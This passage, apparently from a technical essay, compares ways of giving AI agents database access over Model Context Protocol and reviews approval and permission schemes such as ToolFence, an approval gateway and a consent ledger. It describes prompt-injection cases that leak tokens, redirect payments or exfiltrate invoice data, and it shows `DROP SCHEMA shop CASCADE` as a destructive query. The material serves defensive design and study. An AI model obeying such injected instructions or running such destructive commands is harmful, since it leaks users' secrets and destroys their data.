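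Some harder questions also fit. To find actors who appeared in more than one series, the model can have `aggregate_records` count the rows for each actor and keep the counts above one, provided the entity has one row per actor and series. Other requests don't fit:

- **The characters each actor played.** A request names one entity, and `read_records` can't join it to another. Unless `SeriesActors` has a field for characters, the model can't match them to actors in one request.
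- **Voyager actors who never appeared in *The Next Generation*.** SQL can answer this with one query inside another. Here the agent would have to fetch two lists and compare them itself.
- **Deleting every Voyager actor at once.** `delete_record` removes one record, which the model must identify by its key.

Microsoft concedes that joins "aren't an edge case". It advises administrators to create a view that already contains the join or write a stored procedure.

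### Microsoft's case against generated SQL

Microsoft calls it unrealistic to safeguard generated SQL by showing each query to the user first, because this assumes that users know both SQL and the database. It also calls the approach impractical, because people adopt agents to have less to check. It expects overloaded reviewers to approve faulty queries and the business to then rely on the results. This prediction is plausible, since professional testers in an Anthropic experiment approved most of the dangerous shell commands they saw.

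A team can test a fixed interface before release, but it can't certify generated queries in advance. Each query doesn't exist until someone asks a question, and the same question may produce a different query the next day, so the team can only test examples. Unpredictable queries can also slow down a shared database, because administrators build its indexes around the filters they expect.

Microsoft worries more about a query that runs normally and returns the wrong figure than about an agent that deletes a table, which permissions can mostly prevent. Jerry Nixon, who wrote the post, thinks "dropping a table would be better", since people would at least notice. If a wrong sales total looks reasonable, nobody has a reason to correct it.

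*Text-to-SQL Models Make Choices Without Saying So* (2026) supports this worry. It describes models that pick one reading of an ambiguous request without telling the user. The answer is correct for that reading, so a check for faulty SQL finds nothing wrong.

However, SQL MCP Server makes only part of the process predictable. The model has to turn the question into a request, and it can still choose the wrong filter. *Certified Against Which Oracle?* (2026) sorts 288 errors of meaning in generated queries by type. Wrong joins account for 44 and wrong set operations, which combine the results of several queries, for 26. The model can't make those mistakes in an entity request. The other 218 errors (76%) involve filters, aggregates, groupings, sorting or the choice of columns, all of which the model still controls. Wrong filters account for 129 of them. A well-designed view could prevent some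 of these errors, for example by including a column that already shows whether an order is late.

Microsoft is promoting its own product here. Nixon is the program manager for Data API builder, and the post contains no measurements. But the post does recommend generated SQL to developers who are still building a database and have no production data in it. It also recommends generated SQL for exploration, even on production data, if people treat the results as leads to investigate.

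Microsoft also makes an agent for database administrators that writes and runs SQL. It is read-only by default and asks for approval before each query, though users can choose to always allow a tool. Some sample prompts name servers such as `SalesPRD`, presumably a production machine. Microsoft tells these users that the approval system "isn't a security boundary" and that the database's own permissions are. This advice is consistent with the May post if the users are experts, though experts can also miss a wrong filter in a query.

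### Queries with fixed text

A designer can go further and write the whole query in advance. Google's MCP Toolbox for Databases, which developers use to set up such tools, has an example called `search_flights_by_number`:

```sql
SELECT * FROM flights
WHERE airline = $1
AND flight_number = $2
LIMIT 10
```

The model supplies only an airline code and a flight number. According to Google's *postgres-sql*, the database treats them as values, and they can't stand for a table, a column or any other part of the query's structure. The author still has to write the query carefully. This one returns every column, so if the airline later added passengers' names to the table, the tool would return them too.

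The server can get some values from a source other than the model. In another of Google's examples, it takes `user_id` from the person's login. The online shop could do this to let customers ask about their own orders. An injected instruction could not make the agent look up another customer's orders, because the model could not supply that customer's ID.

The Toolbox also has template parameters, which the server pastes into the query before running it. A tool with the text `SELECT * FROM {{.tableName}}` lets the model choose the table, so the tool can read any table the account can. Google warns that template parameters are open to SQL injection and recommends a list of allowed values. *Parameterized query tools usage examples*, from the database company Starburst, describes a similar compromise in which the tool's author fixes the tables and the model chooses among permitted values and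 columns.

Vercel's experiments did not establish how much accuracy an agent would lose without SQL. *From SQL Generation to Tool Selection* (Bogliolo, 2026) tested this with four small models, 17 tasks and a film-rental database.

| Tools available | Average score | Fully correct runs |
|---|---|---|
| Five tools with fixed queries designed for the business | 0.939 | 85% |
| Raw SQL | 0.666 | 33% |
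| Four simple tools for looking up customers, films and rentals | 0.605 | 31% |

The first set of tools did well partly because its queries contained the company's rules. For example, a rental is overdue once its agreed period has passed, but models writing SQL often checked only whether the customer had returned the film. Microsoft describes this kind of quiet error, and an entity request would not necessarily prevent it.

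Bogliolo developed the five tools and the scoring around the same 17 tasks, so the test measures how well fixed queries answer questions their author expected. Stronger models might also narrow the gap. The simple tools are a warning to designers because they prevented the model from writing its own SQL but didn't give it the rules it needed.

### From one question to any question

To compare these designs, suppose the shop's administrator defines an `Orders` entity and lets support staff read two of its fields, `order_id` and `status`. Write *D(r, e)* for the records and fields that role *r* may read in entity *e*. The reach of the reading tool is then:

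*reach(read_records, r) = ⋃ D(r, e), for every entity e that role r may read*

The administrator sets this reach by choosing entities and fields, and the model can act only within it. The table compares this reach with that of the two tools from the original shop example and that of a much looser set of entities.

| Design | What standing approval covers | What the agent can answer |
|---|---|---|
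| Fixed query, `get_order_status` | The status of every order | The status of a given order |
| Entity request, two fields of `Orders` | The number and status of every order | Also how many orders are delayed, or which ones |
| Entity requests, every operation on all 40 tables | All 160 combinations of table and operation, if the user approves each tool | Most questions about one table at a time |
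| `execute_sql` with the owner account | All 160 combinations, plus altering or dropping tables | Any question the data can answer |

Reach and usefulness mostly grow together. The exception is `execute_sql` under the restricted `order_reader` account, which has the same reach as the two-field entity but allows more complicated questions. But entities let the administrator give each role different permissions without creating a database account for each, and they let users read the request without knowing SQL.

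### When everything becomes an entity

An administrator can easily end up in the third row. Microsoft's quick-start example in *Introducing SQL MCP Server* uses the setting `anonymous:*` to give anonymous callers every operation on a `Customers` entity. Repeating that setting for each of the shop's tables would let anonymous callers do nearly everything the owner account can do with SQL, except change the tables' structure.

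The defaults also allow broad access. All seven tools are on, and Microsoft includes every entity unless the administrator excludes it. Microsoft's *What's new in Data API builder version 2.0* (2026) adds that new configurations no longer check who is calling. Until the administrator sets up a login system, every request runs under the anonymous role, so permissions written for support staff have no effect. After that, users inherit the anonymous role's permissions unless the administrator gives them their own.

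Version 2.0 can also create entities automatically. The administrator writes a pattern such as `dbo.%`, which matches every table in SQL Server's default schema, and the server looks for matches each time it starts. If the shop later adds a table called `dbo.staff_salaries`, agents can read it after the next restart. A user who has already clicked "always allow" on `read_records` would see no new prompt. Microsoft offers commands that preview the matching tables and list each role's actual permissions, but someone has to run them to catch the mistake. In November, Microsoft promoted a way to deploy the server in minutes with no configuration file, and therefore no handwritten list of entities.

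The support-ticket attack on Supabase's server could also have worked on Microsoft's if the entity list covered every table with full permissions. The hijacked agent could have fetched the secret tokens with `read_records` and posted them with `create_record`. If the list had covered only tickets and messages, the agent would have had no way to request the tokens.

Broad entity permissions are still somewhat safer than raw SQL. Emptying the orders table takes one `delete_record` call per order, so a user who approves each call has many chances to notice. If the user has given standing approval, the agent can delete every order without asking again. The administrator can switch off `delete_record` for the whole server, and Microsoft notes that some production systems do.

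### The next question nobody prepared for

Raw SQL needs almost no preparation, whereas someone has to define and describe each entity and update it when the tables or business rules change. Field descriptions are optional in SQL MCP Server, but without them `describe_entities` gives the model only the entities' names. If a question needs a new join, someone has to create a view before the model can answer it.

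Bogliolo proposes sending each request that the prepared tools can't answer to an engineer, who writes and reviews a new query that becomes a permanent tool. This relies on prepared tools handling about 95% of requests, a rule of thumb that Bogliolo did not measure. The figure may well hold for support staff who ask about deliveries all day, but is much less likely to hold for an analyst whose questions change every week.

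Adding flexibility reduces the waiting but brings back some of SQL's problems, as Pydantic's engineers found with their parameters. The `filter` argument of `read_records` is already a small query language. Even so, InfoQ (2025) reported that developers had commented on social networks that Data API builder suited only prototypes and simple scenarios. They made those comments before the product included an MCP server.

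Users who can't get an answer may also connect a raw SQL tool. This takes little effort, though how often it happens is unclear. Google's Toolbox includes a ready-made tool for arbitrary SQL, which Google considers generally safe only with a developer involved. Microsoft released an experimental server in 2025. *Introducing MSSQL MCP Server (Preview)* (Vijayraghavan, 2025) described it as a way to talk to a database without writing SQL. The server had tools to create and drop tables, and write access was on by default. According to Strac's *Azure SQL MCP Server* (2026), Microsoft deleted it in June 2026 as unsafe, but copies still circulate. Strac sells a product for controlling such servers, so it has an interest in the warning.

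A user who runs one of those copies next to SQL MCP Server can bypass every entity permission. The administrator can prevent this by making sure the user has no direct database login, or only one with narrow permissions.

The second precaution matters more now that Microsoft lets the server connect to SQL Server as the person using the agent. The database can then record who was responsible for each query and, as with Google's Cloud SQL tool, apply that person's own permissions. But this requires the person to have their own database permissions, which a raw SQL tool could also use. If the entities hide the `Cost` field but the database lets the person read it, the agent could read it too once the person connects a raw SQL tool.

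Bogliolo suggests giving analysts who need SQL access to it under separate credentials. They could then explore a copy of the data freely, while the support agent keeps its prepared tools.

### Approving a request instead of a query

A prompt for `read_records`, unlike one for `execute_sql`, can list the entity, fields and filter separately. Someone who knows no SQL can see that a request for `order_id` and `status` from `Orders` doesn't include home addresses. They may still miss a filter that selects the wrong orders.

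A mistaken approval also does less damage. If a support employee approves a request for `Payments`, the server refuses it unless their role has access. With `execute_sql` and the owner account, nothing checked the request after the employee approved it.

Standing approval is harder to judge. Unlike the same choice for `execute_sql`, "Always allow" on `read_records` doesn't permit deletions. But it covers every entity the role can read, because the host applies approval to the whole tool. A user therefore can't permanently approve order lookups and still review payment lookups.

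The administrator can solve this for common tasks. In version 2.0, a stored procedure can appear as its own named MCP tool, so the shop could offer `get_order_status` as a tool that users could always allow without approving anything else. The prompt would not show the procedure's SQL, so users would have to trust whoever wrote it. That person can at least test the procedure before anyone uses it, whereas the SQL in an `execute_sql` call may have been written only seconds before the user has to approve it.

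## Approval tied to arguments and effects

Prepared queries can't cover every question, so many users will keep a capable tool such as `execute_sql`. Several proposals therefore leave the tool as it is and narrow what each approval covers. Some would change MCP itself so that permissions depend on who is calling or what a particular call does. Three research designs from 2026 tie approval to particular argument values, the exact call that runs, or what that call would complete.

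### Permissions that follow the caller

The July 2026 Model Context Protocol specification lets a server vary its `tools/list` response according to the access token sent with the request, so the server can leave out tools that the token's scopes don't permit. For example, if a shop's support employee has a token that covers only reading orders, the shop's server can hide `delete_order` from the employee's agent. The server must still check the token on every call, because a client could call a hidden tool by name.

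A caller can also start with few scopes and add more later. Model Context Protocol added support for this in November 2025. When a token lacks a scope that a request needs, the server refuses the request and names the missing scope, and the client can then ask the user to grant it. The user considers each permission when a task first needs it, which is easier than judging a long list at installation. But the new scope normally covers later calls too.

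Both mechanisms work well if each tool needs one permission, but `execute_sql` needs different permissions for different queries. Suppose the shop's server has two scopes, `db:read` and `db:write`. If the tool requires `db:write`, an agent that only looks up orders must hold permission to change them. If it requires only `db:read`, an agent with that scope can still run a `DELETE` unless the server inspects the query or runs it under a database account with fewer privileges. Hiding the tool blocks all queries, including order lookups.

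GitHub's developers had the same problem with much less powerful tools. In *SEP-1862*, SamMorrowDrums (2025) wanted GitHub's server to read public repositories without a special scope and request one only for private repositories. With one scope per tool, the server had to request access to everything the tool could reach, even when a user wanted only public data.

### A description of one call

SEP-1862 is a formal proposal to add "tool resolution" to MCP. Before calling a tool, the client would send the server the tool's name and the intended arguments, and the server would describe that particular call. SamMorrowDrums gives the example of a `manage_files` tool that can both read and delete. The tool's fixed labels have to be set to destructive, but with tool resolution the server could label a call with the action `read` as read-only.

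For the shop's SQL tool, the request might look like this:

```json
{
  "method": "tools/resolve",
  "params": {
    "name": "execute_sql",
    "arguments": {
      "query": "SELECT status FROM orders WHERE order_id = 1047"
    }
  }
}
```

The server could label this query read-only and `DROP SCHEMA shop CASCADE` destructive. The host could then run the first without a prompt and ask the user before running the second.

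These labels still wouldn't identify the tables a query reads. SamMorrowDrums suggests a later extension could return the scopes a call needs. A query on the payments table might then require `payments:read`, and one on the orders table only `orders:read`. This would distinguish between calls to `execute_sql` much more usefully than a read-only label.

The server also has to work out what a query does, which can be difficult. Suppose the shop's database has a stored function, `tidy_orders`, that lists orders more than a given number of days late and then deletes them. The query `SELECT tidy_orders(14)` looks like a read. The server could run it inside a database transaction, count the changed rows and cancel the transaction. But that would take about as long as running the query, whereas SamMorrowDrums wants resolution to take milliseconds. Cancelling the transaction also wouldn't undo anything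 the function did outside the database.

An untrustworthy server could falsely label a single call as easily as a whole tool. In a post on annotations, Model Context Protocol (2026) distinguishes hints, which inform a decision, from contracts, which are enforced. The maintainers say that a proposal whose value depends on a label being true belongs in the authorisation layer, the transport or the runtime rather than in annotations. Tool resolution could therefore spare users needless prompts from servers they already trust, but it wouldn't restrain an untrusted server.

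The proposal gained a sponsor and became a draft in February 2026. Model Context Protocol's *Tool Annotations Charter* lists it as a draft and leaves open whether labels should change between calls. In late October, the protocol's list of accepted and final proposals did not include it. The protocol's guidelines require a working prototype and the votes of more than half of the Core Maintainers for acceptance.

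| Mechanism | What can differ | Status |
|---|---|---|
| Tool lists that depend on scopes | The tools each caller sees | Optional in the July 2026 specification |
| Scopes requested when needed | The permissions on a caller's token | In the specification since November 2025 |
| Tool resolution | The description of each call | Draft |

### ToolFence and the recipient of a payment

*ToolFence* (Li, Cao and Xiao, 2026) derives permission from the user's request instead of asking for approval at each call. Suppose a user tells an agent to pay BillPay $100, and the agent has a `send_money(recipient, amount)` tool. The agent then reads a message with a hidden instruction to pay Mallory instead, and it calls `send_money("Mallory", 100)`. The tool is narrow and the task requires it, so neither a list of permitted tools nor standing approval of `send_money` would stop the payment.

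ToolFence writes its rules before the agent reads any outside material. A separate language model sees only the user's request and a reviewed list of tools, and it records the calls that the task needs. For each argument, it chooses one of three rules:

- The value must match the user's request or a trusted record kept by the host.
- The value must come from a particular source, such as a bill the user named.
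- The agent may choose the value.

It also limits how many times the agent can make each call that changes something. Ordinary code then checks every call against these records. In the example, the record permits one payment of $100 to BillPay, so the code rejects the payment to Mallory and would also reject a second payment to BillPay. The hidden instruction can't create a new record. Like Hardy's capabilities, the record both identifies the payee and authorises the payment.

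The first model will sometimes miss a step the task needs. When the agent proposes a call with no matching record, another model decides whether the user's request justifies adding one. It is instructed to refuse if the agent made up a sensitive value, such as an account number.

Li and colleagues tested the system on four collections of simulated attacks. These are the results for Qwen3-max, one of four models they used:

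| Type of attack | Successful attacks without ToolFence | With ToolFence | Harmless tasks completed without ToolFence | With ToolFence |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Instructions in material the agent reads (AgentDojo) | 21.2% | 0% | 66.3% | 64.3% |
| Injected text and false memories (ASB) | 40.2% | 4.2% | 71.5% | 67.2% |
| Instructions in tool descriptions (MCPTox) | 38.1% | 6.1% | 67.2% | 65.4% |
| Instructions spread over many steps (AgentLAB) | 76.3% | 29.4% | 62.4% | 61.1% |

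In a test with Llama 3.3 on the ASB attacks, removing the checks on argument values raised the attack success rate from 5.1% to 24.0%. Removing the model that approves extra steps hardly changed that rate, but it reduced the share of tasks the agent completed under attack from 44.3% to 35.8%.

All four models date from 2025 or earlier. The newest models resist many more injected instructions on their own, so ToolFence would probably prevent fewer attacks on them. The test still shows what ToolFence can do when a model follows an injected instruction.

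Attackers did best when they spread their instructions across several records. Each step then seemed necessary for the task, and the reviewing model sometimes granted too much. In another experiment, ToolFence accepted five of 285 unauthorised calls. All five came from a task in which the user's own request listed the attacker's account as belonging to a "new landlord". ToolFence had recorded the account correctly, but checking where it came from could not show that the user had been deceived.

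ToolFence does not interrupt the user, but it makes the agent slower. Over 200 AgentDojo runs, the mean time rose from 6.3 to 10.3 seconds. CaMeL, an earlier system that also tracks where values come from, took 81.7 seconds. With Qwen3-max, ToolFence also reduced the share of harmless tasks the agent completed by 1.3 to 4.3 percentage points, depending on the task collection.

These results provide little evidence about tools that accept programs. To use ToolFence with `execute_sql`, someone would have to choose a rule for its `query` argument.

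| Rule | `recipient` in `send_money` | `query` in `execute_sql` |
|---|---|---|
| Must match the user's request | Only the payee the user named | Only SQL the user wrote |
| Must come from a named source | The payee in a bill the user named | A saved query in a file the user named |
| The agent may choose | Any account | Any SQL |

The first rule is little help to someone who asks questions in ordinary language and leaves the SQL to the agent. The second is useful if someone has reviewed the saved query, but it limits the agent to what that person prepared. The third would allow `SELECT tidy_orders(14)` or a query for every customer's address.

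ToolFence would work better with Microsoft's `read_records`, which takes the entity, fields and filter as separate arguments. An administrator could fix the entity to `Orders` and let the agent choose the filter. The designer of a tool therefore still determines how precisely ToolFence can limit it.

### Approving the exact call

In *Approve What, Exactly?*, Kodathala, Pollishetty and Cargill (2026) keep user approval but change how the user gives it. They borrow from European rules for online payments, which tie an approval code to the amount and payee the customer sees, so that changing either invalidates the code. They argue that a user's approval of an agent's call should likewise cover exactly the call that runs, and that a compromised agent should be unable to produce the approval itself.

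They built a gateway called ASU, short for Agent Step-Up, which runs outside the agent's computer. When a call needs approval, the process works as follows:

1. The gateway puts the call into a standard form that includes the tool, its arguments and every recipient, account, web address or file path it would affect.
2. It computes a digest, a short fingerprint that changes if any of those details change.
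3. It generates an approval card from the same details, which the user opens on their phone.
4. If the user approves, the phone signs a message that includes the digest.
5. The gateway runs the stored call once. If the agent tries to submit different arguments, the gateway refuses.

The agent can add an explanation, but the gateway's approval card puts it in a separate box marked as untrusted. In one test, a user asked an agent to email a report to their boss. The agent, which was compromised, added a blind copy to an attacker and didn't mention it. All 15 language models acting as approvers accepted the agent's description of the email. All 15 refused when they saw the gateway's card, which listed both recipients.

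MCP's existing confirmation forms offer much weaker protection. In a test of the official Python library, payments of 10 to one account and 10,000 to another produced identical forms, and both ran after acceptance. The library passes on whatever message the server writes. Supabase and AWS use such forms to confirm risky calls, so their users depend on the server to describe each call accurately. The researchers also tested whether agent frameworks let someone change a call after approval, and found that this was possible in four of the eight cases they could measure.

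A test of the card against lies replayed 609 combinations of user tasks and attacks from AgentDojo, with the agent claiming to do what the user had asked. A program simulated the approver.

| What the simulated approver did | Attacks that succeeded with the agent's description | With the gateway's card |
|---|---|---|
| Compared the display with the task | 54% | 3% |
| Believed the agent's explanation | 54% | 54% |

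The card helped only if the approver read the trusted details. For the approver that believed the agent, removing the explanation from the card cut successful attacks to 5%. In a separate test, the 15 language models refused 30% of attacks when shown the agent's description and 98% when shown the card.

No people took part in these experiments. In Anthropic's study, professional testers approved most of the dangerous shell commands even though the prompt displayed them accurately, so the card may help people less than it helped the language models. The finding that binding prevents changes after approval is the strongest result because it doesn't depend on how carefully anyone reads.

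The models also refused 16% of the harmless requests when they saw the card, compared with none when they saw only the agent's description. In most of those refusals, the models cited dummy text the researchers had used, such as `<report placeholder>`. Without those refusals, the rate would have been about 2%. The simulated users completed all 97 harmless tasks with an average of 0.75 approval prompts per task, and the averages for the four groups of tasks ranged from 0.3 to 1.6. The gateway took about 3.5 milliseconds to prepare a request for approval, not counting network delays or the user's time.

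An agent could still repeat requests until the user accepted one, which worked in 45% to 60% of the simulated trials, even with limits on the number of requests. Using a phone instead of a trusted display on the same computer made no measurable difference. However, none of the tests included an attacker who had compromised that display, so the results don't measure how much a separate device would help in that case.

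### The same string with a different effect

The gateway can store both `send_money("BillPay", 100)` and `execute_sql("SELECT tidy_orders(14)")` exactly, and stop the agent from substituting another call after approval. The user can see from the first call who will receive the money and how much, but can't see from the second that `tidy_orders` will delete orders.

The definition of *E(t, a)* used so far leaves out one thing that affects the result. Let *s* be the state of the system when the call runs, including its data and any stored programs. A fuller description of the effect is:

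*E(t, a, s)*

Binding an approval to a call fixes the tool *t* and the arguments *a*, but not *s*. For the payment, the user needs to know fairly little about *s*. For the query, *s* includes the code of `tidy_orders`. If a database administrator changed that function after the user approved the query, the gateway would run the approved text with a different result.

Shell commands have the same problem. ASU stores a command as a list of arguments and adds a warning when the command contains code for an interpreter, as in `bash -c` or `python -c`. The warning doesn't describe what the code will do, and a command that only names a script, such as `python count_orders.py`, doesn't trigger it. A designer could include a digest of the script in the approval, but the script might still read other files or fetch instructions from the internet.

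Standing approval needs particular care. ASU's "allow similar" option keeps the recipient fixed but can let amounts vary up to a limit and free text vary up to a certain length. Free text that varies is reasonable in an email message, but if an operator classified `query` as free text, "allow similar" could cover any SQL within the length limit.

### What an action completes

A user can understand a call and still miss the harm because it depends on earlier calls. *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues, 2026) describes a user who asks an agent to check supplier invoices and send an auditor only the summary totals. A hidden instruction in a supplier's note makes the agent put every line of the invoices in a file called `report.csv`, which it then asks permission to send to the auditor. The tool, recipient and file name all look right, but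 the file contains data the user said not to send.

Their system, the Cumulative Consent Ledger, records what the agent's tools actually do and where each file's contents came from. If a tool creates a new item *z′* from inputs *z₁* to *zₖ*, the ledger keeps the origins of all of them:

*L(z′) ⊇ L(z₁) ∪ L(z₂) ∪ … ∪ L(zₖ)*

Here *L* is the set of sources behind an item. The rule may include a source whose data the tool never copied, but it prevents sensitive data from going untracked in the ledger. Before an important action, a monitor compares the likely result with the user's original restrictions and classifies the action as allowed, a violation or unknown.

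The approval screen shows the user's original instruction, the exact action and a sentence about the result, but not this verdict. In the invoice example, the user reads that the agent built the attachment from raw invoice rows and that sending it would transfer those rows to the auditor. The user can open the records that sentence is based on.

Hossain and colleagues tested the screen with 80 volunteers. Each person used one of four designs and judged six harmless and six unsafe requests.

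| What the volunteers saw | Unsafe requests approved | Harmless requests approved | Median time per decision |
|---|---|---|---|
| A short description of the action | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 seconds |
| The exact arguments as well | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 seconds |
| The arguments, the user's instruction and a log of earlier steps | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 seconds |
| The same facts, with the result explained | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 seconds |

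The second design is closest to what the MCP specification recommends, yet its users still approved more than two in five unsafe requests. Most of the improvement over the short description came from extra information. The last two designs contained the same facts, so comparing them isolates the effect of explaining the result. After adjustment, unsafe approvals were 7.9 percentage points lower with the explanation, but the 95% interval ran from a reduction of 19.7 points to an increase of 3.8, so the study doesn't establish that the explanation helped.

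The new screen took about twice as long to use as a short description, and people using it rejected harmless requests slightly more often. Half of the requests were unsafe, which may have made the volunteers more alert than people who rarely see an attack. People approved seven of the 30 violations that depended on several linked steps, whether they used the log or the new screen.

The researchers also let the monitor block actions without asking anyone. In 240 runs across two small language models, the number of attacks that caused an unsafe effect fell from 110 to 13. The agents completed 206 of 240 harmless tasks, down from 214. Each check took a median of 24 milliseconds. These results depend on the monitor receiving a complete record of what the tools do. When the record was incomplete and the monitor blocked every unknown action, the agents completed only 76.7% of harmless tasks.

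A payment tool can report the recipient and amount in a form that is easy to record in the ledger. For `execute_sql`, recording the effects would require working out which tables and rows each query read or changed. In the Supabase attack, a single SQL statement could have copied secret tokens into a customer's ticket. If the monitor had been able to interpret that statement, the approval screen could have shown the developer that the reply would contain the tokens, which would have been much more useful than the SQL alone.

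For `SELECT tidy_orders(14)`, the monitor would need to predict what the stored function will do. If it couldn't, it should return "unknown". Hossain and colleagues suggest showing such cases to the user with an explanation of the missing evidence, instead of always blocking them. An agent that mostly runs SQL or shell commands might produce many of these prompts, and the user would still have to decide without knowing what the program will do.
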